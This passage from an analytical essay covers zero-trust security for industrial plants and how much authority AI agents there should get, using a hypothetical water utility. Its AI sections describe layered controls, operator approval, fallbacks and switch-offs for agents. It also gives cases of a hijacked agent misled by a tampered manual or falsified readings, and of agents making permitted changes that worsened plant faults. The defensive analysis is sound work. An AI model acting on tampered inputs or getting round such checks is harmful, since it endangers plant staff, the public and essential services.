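CISA warns that time-limited access must be granted promptly, because staff who have to wait may set up their own unofficial connections. The jump host is also an obvious target, since an attacker who controls it can reach everything behind it. The utility has to patch the jump host much more often than the PLCs, which is possible because restarting it doesn't stop a pump.

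### Scans that can stop a controller

Zero trust depends on knowing which devices are on the network. In an office, a scanner finds them by sending test messages to every address. CISA warns that this can knock old industrial devices offline, and notes that plants generally rely on passive monitoring instead. Passive monitoring equipment identifies devices from a copy of the normal traffic, without sending them anything.

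Scanning may be less dangerous than its reputation suggests. In *Safe Active Scanning for Energy Delivery Systems*, Helms, Salazar and colleagues (2017) scanned 38 devices at three US national laboratories, and one malfunctioned and needed a restart. Their conclusion that scanning is unlikely to harm the safety of energy systems seems too optimistic, because at the same rate a plant with 200 devices would have about five failures. With only 38 devices tested, the true rate could be as high as 14%.

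Their results are still a good argument against banning scans altogether, because passive monitoring can't detect a device that sends nothing. It could miss an idle backup controller or an intruder's device that isn't transmitting. CISA accepts active scans that use industrial protocols or target newer components. The utility could first scan a spare PLC on a workbench, then scan the station during a planned outage.

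### Signing before encryption

Signing keeps an outsider from changing a pump's speed, which matters more than hiding the speed with encryption. CISA therefore puts signing ahead of encryption, which can add delay and complexity. It still wants encryption for data that enters or leaves the control network, especially over a telephone company's lines.

Signing without encryption also lets monitoring equipment read the traffic. ISAGCA's *Zero Trust Outcomes Using ISA/IEC 62443 Standards* (2024), a white paper from an industrial security alliance, suggests using TLS with encryption turned off, which still lets two devices authenticate each other and detect altered messages.

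But signing also takes time. Under the electricity standard IEC 61850, certain protection messages must take no more than 3 milliseconds from end to end, and Help Net Security reports that operators feared slower devices couldn't sign them in time. The advice to sign first is therefore easier to follow at a pumping station than in parts of the power grid.

Certificates cause another problem because they expire. If a PLC rejected expired certificates as strictly as a web browser does, it could stop accepting commands from the control room because someone forgot to renew a certificate. CISA considers signing safer than full encryption here, since an expired certificate won't halt operations if the messages remain readable. But this is true only if the receiving device is set to accept signatures from expired certificates. Otherwise, it will reject messages even though it can read them.

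Some operators have considered leaving certificate expiry checks off at first and tightening them later. A more precise rule would be to raise an alarm when a certificate expires and still accept the commands that keep water flowing, but refuse new PLC programs until someone renews the certificate. The utility would risk an attacker using a stolen old key, but only to send routine commands.

### When the policy decision point fails

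If the server that makes the utility's access decisions crashes, the enforcement points can either refuse all requests (fail closed) or allow them all (fail open). NERC considers failing closed appropriate in most office systems, but it rules out a plant-wide fail-closed policy because some critical systems have to keep communicating and blocking them could kill people.

| Request during the failure | If refused | If allowed |
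|---|---|---|
| A manufacturer's engineer wants a remote session to tune pump 4 | The tuning waits until morning | An intruder could get the same access and reprogram the PLC |
| An operator orders an emergency shutdown of pump 4 because a main has burst | Water keeps flooding the street | An intruder already on the network could stop the pump |

The utility should refuse the remote session and allow the shutdown. If remote sessions were allowed whenever the server was down, an attacker could crash it to get in. A malicious shutdown is also a risk, but staff at the station can restart the pump, whereas nobody can undo an injury caused by a late shutdown.

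If the engineer's session is already open when the server fails, cutting it off could leave the PLC with half a new program, so staff at the station should decide when to end it. Stopping equipment can also be unsafe. A pump that drains a tunnel, for example, may need to keep running. The engineers who know the process have to decide in advance which state is safe, and the exception should cover only the command that leads to that state. A request to raise the pump's speed can still fail closed.

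Ideally, an emergency shutdown doesn't depend on the decision server. Many chemical plants and refineries have a safety instrumented system, with its own sensors and logic, that brings the process to a safe state when a reading crosses a set limit. It is often independent of the ordinary control system, so a failure in the control system doesn't disable it. A stop button wired directly to the pump's motor is a simpler version.

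For everyday work, the utility can run a second decision server or give each station a local copy of the rules. With a local copy, the operators on shift could keep adjusting the pumps during a server failure. The copy could be out of date, so an employee dismissed that evening might still have access until the server came back. That risk is probably acceptable at a pumping station if it keeps the water on.

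### Break-glass access

Operators may also need to do something urgent that no rule covers, when their normal logins don't work. CISA calls emergency access "non-negotiable" and suggests break-glass accounts. These accounts have wide permissions, and staff use them only in an emergency.

North station could keep the password in a sealed envelope in the control room. An operator opens the envelope and logs in, which alerts the supervisor. The system records everything the operator does, and access ends after about an hour unless someone extends it. The next day, the supervisor reviews the recording, changes the password and seals the new one in an envelope.

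The control system has to check this password itself, because the central login server may have failed. The utility should test the account regularly. It can also make the password work only from the control room's own keyboards, so that a thief can't use it over the internet. CISA notes that physical access already serves as a second factor in many plants.

A break-glass account, which is kept for emergencies, bypasses the normal access rules, so its security depends on people using it rarely and on someone reviewing each use. If operators use it every week, their ordinary login is probably too slow or too restrictive.

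### Why a remote check can't sit inside a control loop

Suppose the PLC at North station repeats its cycle every 10 milliseconds. These timings are invented for illustration.

| Step | Time |
|---|---|
| Read the pressure and flow sensors | 1 ms |
| Calculate the new pump speed | 3 ms |
| Send the speed to the motor | 1 ms |
| Spare time | 5 ms |

Now suppose the PLC needs approval from a decision server in another city before it changes the speed. It sends the request 4 milliseconds into the cycle. The message takes 20 milliseconds to travel there and back, and the server needs 5 to answer, so the reply arrives at 29 milliseconds, when the cycle should have ended at 10. By then the pressure may have changed, and the approved speed may be wrong.

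A faster policy engine wouldn't solve this, because the journey alone takes twice as long as the whole cycle.

A server inside the station might usually answer within the 5 spare milliseconds, but the PLC runs 100 cycles a second, or 8.64 million a day. Even if 99.99% of the answers arrived on time, 864 a day would be late, and each time the PLC would have to skip an adjustment or make it without permission. A control loop needs every answer on time, so the server's average response time is the wrong measure.

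The check can happen outside the loop instead. An operator may change the target pressure a few times a day, and nobody would notice a delay of 25 milliseconds. The same applies to loading a new program. The policy then controls who may change the PLC's instructions, while the PLC carries them out without checking permission each time. CISA also suggests separate permissions for individual values in a PLC, so an operator could change the target pressure but only read the temperature at which the motor cuts out.

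### Does industrial segmentation already achieve this?

Plants divided their networks into separate parts long before Kindervag proposed zero trust. ISA/IEC 62443, the main family of standards for industrial security, calls these parts zones and the controlled channels between them conduits. Each zone groups equipment with the same security needs. The PLCs at North station could form one zone and its safety system another, with a conduit that lets two named control room computers reach the PLCs.

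ISAGCA argues that the standards already supply much of zero trust. It matches zones to the resources that zero trust protects and conduits to the permitted flows of traffic, and it finds requirements for identity, least privilege and continuous monitoring. The standards also prohibit security measures from interfering with safety functions, control of the process, or an operator's ability to see and operate the equipment, unless a risk assessment supports it.

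ISAGCA concludes that components built to these standards already have the security functions that zero trust needs. Two of the paper's four authors worked for Schneider Electric and Rockwell Automation, which sell industrial control equipment, so they had an interest in that conclusion. A plant can also own a security function for years without turning it on, as happened with secure protocols. But the comparison is useful, because a utility with well-designed zones has already done much of the work of listing its equipment and deciding what needs to communicate.

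NERC suggests dividing equipment on the same Purdue level into several zones, such as one for each substation. An attacker who takes over one substation then has to get through another firewall to reach the next. But Stouffer and colleagues point out that firewalls between zones don't stop an attacker from moving around within one. If the PLCs at North accept any command from their own zone, they still grant access based on network location alone, which zero trust is meant to prevent.

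Segmentation also gets weaker over time. A utility might add a firewall rule so that a contractor's laptop can reach the PLCs, then forget to remove it when the work ends. After a few years of such exceptions, the network may no longer match its diagram. Someone can also carry malware past every firewall on a USB stick. CISA therefore wants organisations to treat segmentation as a policy they keep enforcing rather than a one-time design decision.

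Attackers can also get in with stolen logins. When it announced the guide, CISA (2026) said it had seen groups such as Volt Typhoon, which the US government links to China, targeting industrial systems to gain and keep access. If a plant and its business offices share a login system, an attacker who steals passwords in the offices may be able to use them in the plant. A firewall can let this connection through because it breaks no rules, so CISA recommends keeping the two login systems completely separate.

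ISAGCA and NERC disagree about how useful partial zero trust is. ISAGCA accepts gradual improvement but warns that zero trust doesn't work if it covers only some parts of a plant, because attackers will find the rest. NERC expects a mixture of old and new controls for years, and thinks some old sites may never be worth converting. NERC's position is more realistic for a utility with 20-year-old PLCs, but ISAGCA's warning is a good reason to list the unprotected parts and watch them more closely.

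Industrial traffic is at least easier to monitor than office traffic, because it is repetitive. If the historian reads the same values from the same PLC every few seconds, a command from an unfamiliar laptop stands out. The utility can also compare its firewall rules with its actual traffic. A rule that has gone unused for six months may be left over from a contractor's visit, but it could also permit the link to the backup control room, so an engineer who knows the station should check it before anyone deletes it.

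## What should a model in an industrial plant be allowed to read and change?

The utility's maintenance agent can read pump history and propose new pump settings. The utility could give it less authority or considerably more.

| Degree of authority | What the model does at North station | If the model is wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Reads exported data | Forecasts wear on pump 4 from a copy of the historian | The planner may schedule a needless repair |
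| Advises an operator | Displays a suggestion to run pump 4 more slowly | The operator may follow bad advice |
| Proposes a change | Fills in the new speed, which takes effect only if an operator accepts it | The operator may accept it without looking |
| Changes settings directly | Sends the new speed to the PLC | The pump changes speed before anyone has looked |

Yokogawa (2025), a Japanese automation company, announced that several of its AI agents now directly control the removal of acid gas at Aramco's Fadhili gas plant in Saudi Arabia. Yokogawa trained these agents, which aren't language models, by trial and error (reinforcement learning) in a simulator. It introduced them in three phases and connected them to the plant's existing control system to keep its safety functions.

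Language models usually have less authority. According to CISA, companies typically use them in business systems, perhaps on data exported from the plant, and use predictive models closer to the equipment. Vendors are now bringing agents into the control room. Chemical Online's *ControlRooms Unveils First Agentic Troubleshooting System For Chemical & Energy Operations* reports that in September 2026 ControlRooms launched four agents that detect production problems and advise staff on how to resolve them. Hydrocarbon Processing's *Honeywell introduces Experion Cognition to deliver autonomous control room operations* (2026) describes a more ambitious product, for the petrochemical company Borouge International. "Autonomous" is a vague term, so a buyer should ask which settings such a product can change without an operator.

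### Getting data out without letting anyone in

In December 2025 CISA, Australia's ASD and seven other agencies published guidance on AI in industrial plants. They prefer designs in which the plant pushes data out and the AI system has no lasting connection into the plant. At the utility, this could work as follows:

1. The historian sends selected readings to a staging server in the buffer zone (DMZ).
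2. The staging server logs what leaves and passes it on.
3. The agent reads the copy on the business network.

Some plants add a data diode, a device whose hardware can transmit data in only one direction. An attacker who hijacks the agent could then read the copied data but couldn't use the same link to reach a PLC.

The agent can read only what the utility has chosen to send from the plant, and it may get the data late. The utility has to choose carefully, because exported data can leak. CISA warns that network diagrams and control logic stay useful to attackers for years, and that a model trained on process readings may retain those readings. The agent needs pump 4's vibration and temperature but not a map of the station's network.

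A proposed change needs a separate path back into the plant. The agent could put its proposal in a queue in the buffer zone, and the control room's software could collect it from there, so every connection would still start from inside the plant.

The guidance is strictest about physical safety. It says language models "almost certainly should not be used to make safety decisions" in plants, because they can invent plausible data and may be too unreliable to make critical decisions independently. A language model could still draft a work order. Pump speeds are a less clear case, because a change that normally saves electricity could become a safety decision if a main bursts.

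### One pump change, layer by layer

Suppose pump 4 is running at 1,450 revolutions per minute (rpm) and vibrating at 6.0 mm/s. The agent proposes slowing it to 1,300 rpm until technicians can replace the bearing. The limits below are invented.

1. **Identity.** The queue accepts the proposal only with a valid token for the agent and planner P-117. The log records the agent under its own identity, which CISA wants kept distinct from those of users and ordinary machines.
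2. **Policy.** The agent may propose speeds for North's pumps, but only a control room operator may commit one.
3. **Data check.** Software confirms that the vibration reading is recent and that the bearing temperature is consistent with it.
4. **Physical limits.** The PLC accepts speeds from 1,200 to 1,500 rpm, changes speed by at most 50 rpm a minute, and refuses any reduction while the pressure in the mains is below 3 bar. The control room's software tests the proposal against the same limits first, so the operator never sees an impossible one.
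5. **Operator approval.** The operator sees the present and proposed speeds, the evidence and the expected pressure. If the operator accepts, the PLC applies its limits again, because the pressure may have changed in the meantime.
6. **Independent safety system.** If the pressure falls below 2 bar, a separate switch starts a standby pump. Another switch stops pump 4 if the pressure gets dangerously high. Neither switch takes commands from the agent or the PLC.

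| What goes wrong | What should stop it | What remains if that fails |
|---|---|---|
| A tampered manual makes the agent request 2,400 rpm | The PLC's speed limit | The high-pressure switch |
| A falsified reading shows vibration of 3.0, so the agent proposes speeding up to 1,500 rpm | The data check, because the bearing is too hot for that reading | An operator who knows the pump |
| The agent proposes 1,250 rpm on true data, but pump 7 is out for repair and evening demand is about to rise | The operator, who knows about pump 7 | The low-pressure switch |

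The identity check stops none of these, because the utility's own agent makes all three requests. Policy matters most if the hijacked agent tries to send a command itself, which it has no permission to do.

A bad recommendation that looks plausible is the hardest kind to stop. It passes every automatic check because the pressure is still normal when the agent proposes it. The safety system is a good last resort, but it covers only the hazards that engineers anticipated, and no switch in this example would prevent a higher speed from wrecking the worn bearing.

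### When a permitted change makes a fault worse

In *OperAItor*, Vyas and Mercangöz (2026) tested language-model agents on a simulated chemical plant with a reactor and a distillation column. The agents could start standby pumps and change production rates and other targets, but they couldn't bypass 11 independent safety interlocks.

In one test, the agent lowered the target level of a leaking tank. It was allowed to make this change, which might have been harmless under other conditions, but the control system responded by drawing more liquid out of the tank. An interlock stopped the plant at about minute 23 of the simulation, compared with minute 46 when no agent intervened.

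A fixed range for the target can't prevent this, because the right value depends on whether the tank is leaking. Vyas and Mercangöz therefore compared several ways to check a proposal before it takes effect. One uses a second call to the same model to review the proposal. Another simulates the next 30 minutes with and without the change. A third applies fixed rules that require the agent to cite trusted evidence, have authority for the action and follow the written procedure. The table shows how many of 20 fault scenarios ended in a plant stop.

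| Check | GPT-5 nano | Qwen3 8B | Mistral 7B | Llama 3.2 3B |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 7 | 7 | 7 | 13 |
| Second model call | 6 | 7 | 7 | 15 |
| Simulation | 7 | 7 | 7 | 12 |
| Fixed rules | 5 | 8 | 7 | 7 |
| Fixed rules and simulation | 7 | 7 | 7 | 9 |

Without an agent, 18 scenarios ended in a stop. The choice of check made little difference except with Llama, the weakest model, where fixed rules cut the stops from 13 to 7. That drop may be partly because filling in the required form prompted the agent to act. When a single pump failed, Llama did nothing without the rules but started the standby pump within two and a half minutes with them. Each combination ran only once per scenario, so differences of one or two stops could easily be chance.

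The drop from 18 stops also overstates the agents' benefit, because the baseline was an almost unattended control room. A human operator would normally start a standby pump too. And the simulation paused the plant while the models made decisions, which took between 8 and 405 seconds on average, depending on the model and the check. In the fastest-moving scenario, the plant stopped about seven minutes after a pump failed, so the slowest combination of model and check would have used nearly all of that time.

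### Sequences of safe-looking changes

*Bounded Supervisory Autonomy With Large Reasoning Models for Abnormal Situation Management* (Alhazmi, 2026) compares language models with conventional automation, a comparison OperAItor lacks. Alhazmi, who works for the chemical company SABIC, tested both on the same disturbances in the Tennessee Eastman process, a standard simulated plant. The models had supervisory authority, so they could adjust targets, switch on existing control functions, run approved procedures or shut the plant down, but they couldn't move valves directly.

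Each system faced 39 simulated runs of 48 hours. In 15 of them, the right decision was to do nothing.

| System in charge | Runs completed without a trip | Runs with needless action, of 15 | Average production, m³ |
|---|---|---|---|
| Basic control only | 24 | 0 | 754 |
| Full conventional control | 39 | 0 | 1,123 |
| Simple scripted rules | 39 | 4 | 961 |
| Claude Sonnet-5, high effort | 39 | 9 | 999 |
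| Claude Sonnet-5, low effort | 38 | 7 | 987 |
| GLM-5.2 | 37 | 12 | 1,001 |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 39 | 12 | 1,058 |

The models were much better than basic control, but full conventional control also prevented every trip, produced more and never acted needlessly. The models did identify the cause of a disturbance far more often than the scripted rules, which suggests they may be more useful for diagnosis than for control.

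Each of the three trips under the models came from a series of changes that had individually passed the checks. In one, GLM-5.2 responded to a disturbance that basic control would have handled on its own. It made five changes in less than six hours, which together drained a vessel and tripped the plant at hour 16.5. The check simulated each change for six hours, and the harm took longer to appear.

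Alhazmi recommends checking whole sequences of changes and comparing the plant's response with the prediction after each one. If the two diverge, control should pass to a person or to fixed logic. At the utility, the agent might have to wait until the pressure settles before proposing another speed. Alhazmi would also block changes when the plant is already heading for a safe result. In a small pilot, such a block reduced the share of time the model could run the plant without an operator from 100% to 41%.

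The data a model can read also affects how it acts. In one scenario, Sonnet-5 received a summary that listed the target composition and the measurement separately, and it left the product 13.6 percentage points off target. When Alhazmi added the difference between the two to the summary, the error fell to 0.2 points with the same model and instructions. The utility should therefore test the summary of plant data given to the agent as carefully as it tests the agent's permissions.

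Both studies made their forecasts using a perfect copy of the simulated plant, which no real plant has. Gopali, Chhetri and colleagues (2026), in *Neuro-Agentic Control*, used recorded data from SWaT, an experimental water treatment plant, and added simulated attacks. Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite proposed how fast and how long to drain a tank, and a forecasting model tested whether this would keep the level below a critical threshold. The level stayed below the threshold in five of 15 trials, compared with four and two with other forecasting models.

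No physically invalid action took effect, but the rules define "valid" loosely. They allow a drain of 60 mm per time step for 50 steps, or 3,000 mm in total, although the tank's critical level is 1,000 mm. The software then picks the proposal with the lowest forecast peak. The published rule does not stop it from emptying the tank, but a PLC limit on the minimum level would.

### Choosing from approved playbooks

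An agent doesn't need permission to write individual settings if it can choose a procedure that engineers have already tested. Malik, Jayasinghe and colleagues at Microsoft propose this arrangement in *Decentralized Granular Access Control for Agentic AI Systems in Critical Infrastructure* (2026). The infrastructure they describe is a large cloud provider's network equipment, not pumps or power lines.

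Their agents can read from network devices but never write to them. If an agent finds a fault, it requests a playbook, a fixed series of steps that engineers have reviewed and tested. The playbook has its own limited write permission. The riskiest changes need approval from several people, and an agent can't start that process.

Before each call, the system checks the agent's general access, the tool, the particular function, the values and the circumstances. A rule about circumstances might allow a call only during an open incident and for at most ten devices. The agent's access also can't exceed that of the person it works for.

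The proposal is decentralised because each team writes the policies for the tools it owns. At the utility, the pump engineers, who know what the equipment can tolerate, would set the pump limits. The median time to change a policy fell from 5.3 days to 0.8 after the cloud provider switched to this method. But the teams need enough security knowledge to write sound policies, which Malik and colleagues acknowledge as a weakness.

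The system recorded no unauthorised writes in eight months with more than 20 agents, and blocked all 47 detected attempts to gain extra privileges. It wrongly refused 0.3% of legitimate requests. The absence of unauthorised writes is less impressive than it sounds, because the agents had no permission to write to devices and an authorised playbook that ran at the wrong moment wouldn't be counted.

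The idea should work fairly well in a plant. A playbook at North could start pump 7, wait for steady pressure and then slow pump 4, stopping if the pressure leaves its normal range. *LLM-Driven Multi-Agent Control for Skill-Based Smart Manufacturing* (2026) describes a possible connection, in which agents use MCP to call a machine's predefined skills through OPC UA, an industrial communication standard. The cloud system requires the person behind the agent to have an active session, so at night the utility's agent would have to work for the operator on shift instead of the planner.

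### False alarms and outside connections

A model that only gives advice can still cause harm if it raises too many false alarms. Suppose it checks 200 pumps every hour and wrongly flags 1% of the healthy ones each time, which adds up to about 48 false alarms a day. If one pump a week starts to fail, the operators get about 336 false alarms for each true one and will probably stop reading the alarms.

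Operators may already have too many alarms. Automation World's *Emerson Helps Romanian Refinery Cut DCS Alarm Volumes by More Than 95%* (2026) shows that one refinery could do without most of its alarms. The utility should measure its current alarm load before adding a model, and reduce that load if necessary. CISA recommends comparing a model's false alarms with the number of real faults, as in the calculation above. After that comparison, the 1% error rate no longer looks good. Operators who approve changes can also tire, just as office workers can when approving an agent's commands, so too many harmless proposals would make their reviews less careful.

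The utility may acquire a model without meaning to. Cassels (2026), in *Emerson adds AI agents to engineering, production software*, reports that Emerson, a major supplier of control systems, is adding agents to existing products. CISA warns that some industrial devices now contain AI that may need an internet connection. If the utility allows data to flow only outward but then installs a controller that contacts its manufacturer's cloud, it reopens an inbound route to the plant.

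CISA advises buyers to ask where the model runs, whether it can work without the vendor's cloud, and whether the vendor will train on their data. The contract should let the operator turn off the AI features. It should also require the vendor to tell customers if it discovers that the model can give improper advice. Any remaining connection should go through the plant's existing buffer zone or jump host.

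### Switching a model off

CISA recommends setting thresholds in advance for returning to conventional control if a model drifts. The utility might set the PLC to stop accepting the model's targets if the model's pressure forecasts are wrong by more than 0.3 bar for ten minutes. *A Tutorial on Autonomous Fault-Tolerant Control Using Knowledge-Grounded LLM Agents* (Vyas, Gill and colleagues, 2026) includes upkeep among the constraints on using models in plants, and that upkeep would include setting new thresholds after each major repair.

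If an office agent misbehaves, a company can usually revoke its access at once and sort out the consequences later. In a plant, suddenly revoking a model's access can disturb the process. Suppose a model controls the power of pump 4's motor and has set it to 70%. If the PLC takes over and immediately sets 64%, the pressure drops unnecessarily.

Control engineers avoid this with bumpless transfer, which OperAItor uses when a control loop goes from manual to automatic operation. A common type of controller calculates its output as

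u = b + K·e + I

where b is the normal output, e is the gap between the target and the measurement, and K determines how strongly the controller reacts to that gap. I is a correction that builds up over time. At the moment of transfer, the controller sets

I = u_now − b − K·e

so that its first output equals the present one. If b is 60 and K·e is 4, then I starts at 70 − 60 − 4 = 6, and the motor stays at 70%. With I at zero, the output would have jumped to 64%. The controller then moves gradually towards its own target.

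This is suitable if the model has only become inaccurate. If an attacker controls the model, the current output may be dangerous, so the PLC should move to a known safe speed as quickly as the pipes can tolerate.

The utility also needs a fallback in case the model is too slow. *From Detection to Action* (Vyas, Gill and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that hands control to a separate safety function if the agents don't find an acceptable plan within a fixed time. The time limit has to be short enough that the safety function still has time to act.

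All of this assumes that someone can run the plant without the model. CISA warns that staff who rely on AI may lose that skill. The utility could schedule regular shifts with the model off, which would also test the transfer while nothing else is wrong.

### How much control is worth giving?

The best argument for direct control is efficiency. Yokogawa reported that Fadhili used 10% to 15% less steam and amine, the chemical that absorbs the acid gas, and about 5% less electricity, and that operators intervened much less often. These are initial figures from the company that sells the system, but savings of that size would matter to any large plant. Evonik, a German chemical company, also reports using AI to save energy and reduce carbon emissions at its Oxeno plants. A person can't make small adjustments all day and night, and requiring someone to approve each one would cancel much of the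 benefit.

Staffing is another reason. ControlRooms argues that plants are losing knowledge as experienced operators retire. It has a product to sell, but the concern is reasonable. A small utility may also have only one person on duty at night.

Advice is enough for many tasks, though. A forecast of bearing wear is just as useful if a person orders the replacement the next morning. CISA also recommends that owners consider whether established technology would do the job before they choose AI. Alhazmi's results support that recommendation, since well-tuned conventional control produced more than any of the language models. Advice also carries risk, because an operator who accepts every suggestion has in effect given the model direct control.

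The agents at Fadhili are specialised controllers that Yokogawa trained for one process, so they don't show that a language model should control a plant. The utility could reasonably let a similar controller adjust pump speeds to save electricity, within the PLC's limits and after a long trial in which it only gave advice. The maintenance agent reads manuals and emails that an attacker can tamper with, and it doesn't need to act within seconds, so it should work from exported data and propose playbooks for an operator to start.
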